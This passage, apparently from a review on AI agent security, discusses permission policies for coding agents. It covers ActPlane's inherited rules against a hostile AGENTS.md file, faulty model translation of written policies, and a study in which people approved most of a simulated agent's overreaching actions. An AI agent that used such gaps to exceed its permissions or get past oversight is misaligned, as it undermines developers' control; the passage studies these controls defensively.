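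The exact percentages may not hold elsewhere, because Zheng and colleagues favoured recent projects about AI agents. They also used language models to classify the statements, though people checked a sample of 100. The main finding should still hold, because projects differ in their test commands, private folders and deployment servers. A vendor can still supply a few general rules, such as one that keeps SSH keys away from install-time code.

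ActPlane lets the agent fill in the project's details. This is safe only because ActPlane's policy domains stop the agent from removing inherited rules, so a hostile `AGENTS.md` could at worst stop the agent from working. A rule that grants something, such as permission to upload to a particular server, has to come from someone the developer trusts. Translating written policies into formal ones is another weak point. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that existing tools typically have a language model do this without validating the result, and bad translations caused most of ActPlane's missed violations.

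Leaving the rules to each developer has drawbacks too. Wu and colleagues found that the freedom developers gave their agents varied much more between individuals than between kinds of work, and they recommend that teams agree on permissions together. Salerno and colleagues also describe an experiment by Yan in which 113 people supervised a simulated day of an agent's actions. Rules the participants wrote themselves blocked less overreach than either approval of each action or automated review by a model. For most of their rules, participants had chosen "ask", which postponed the decision until the agent tried to act. They then explicitly approved most of the actions that went too far.
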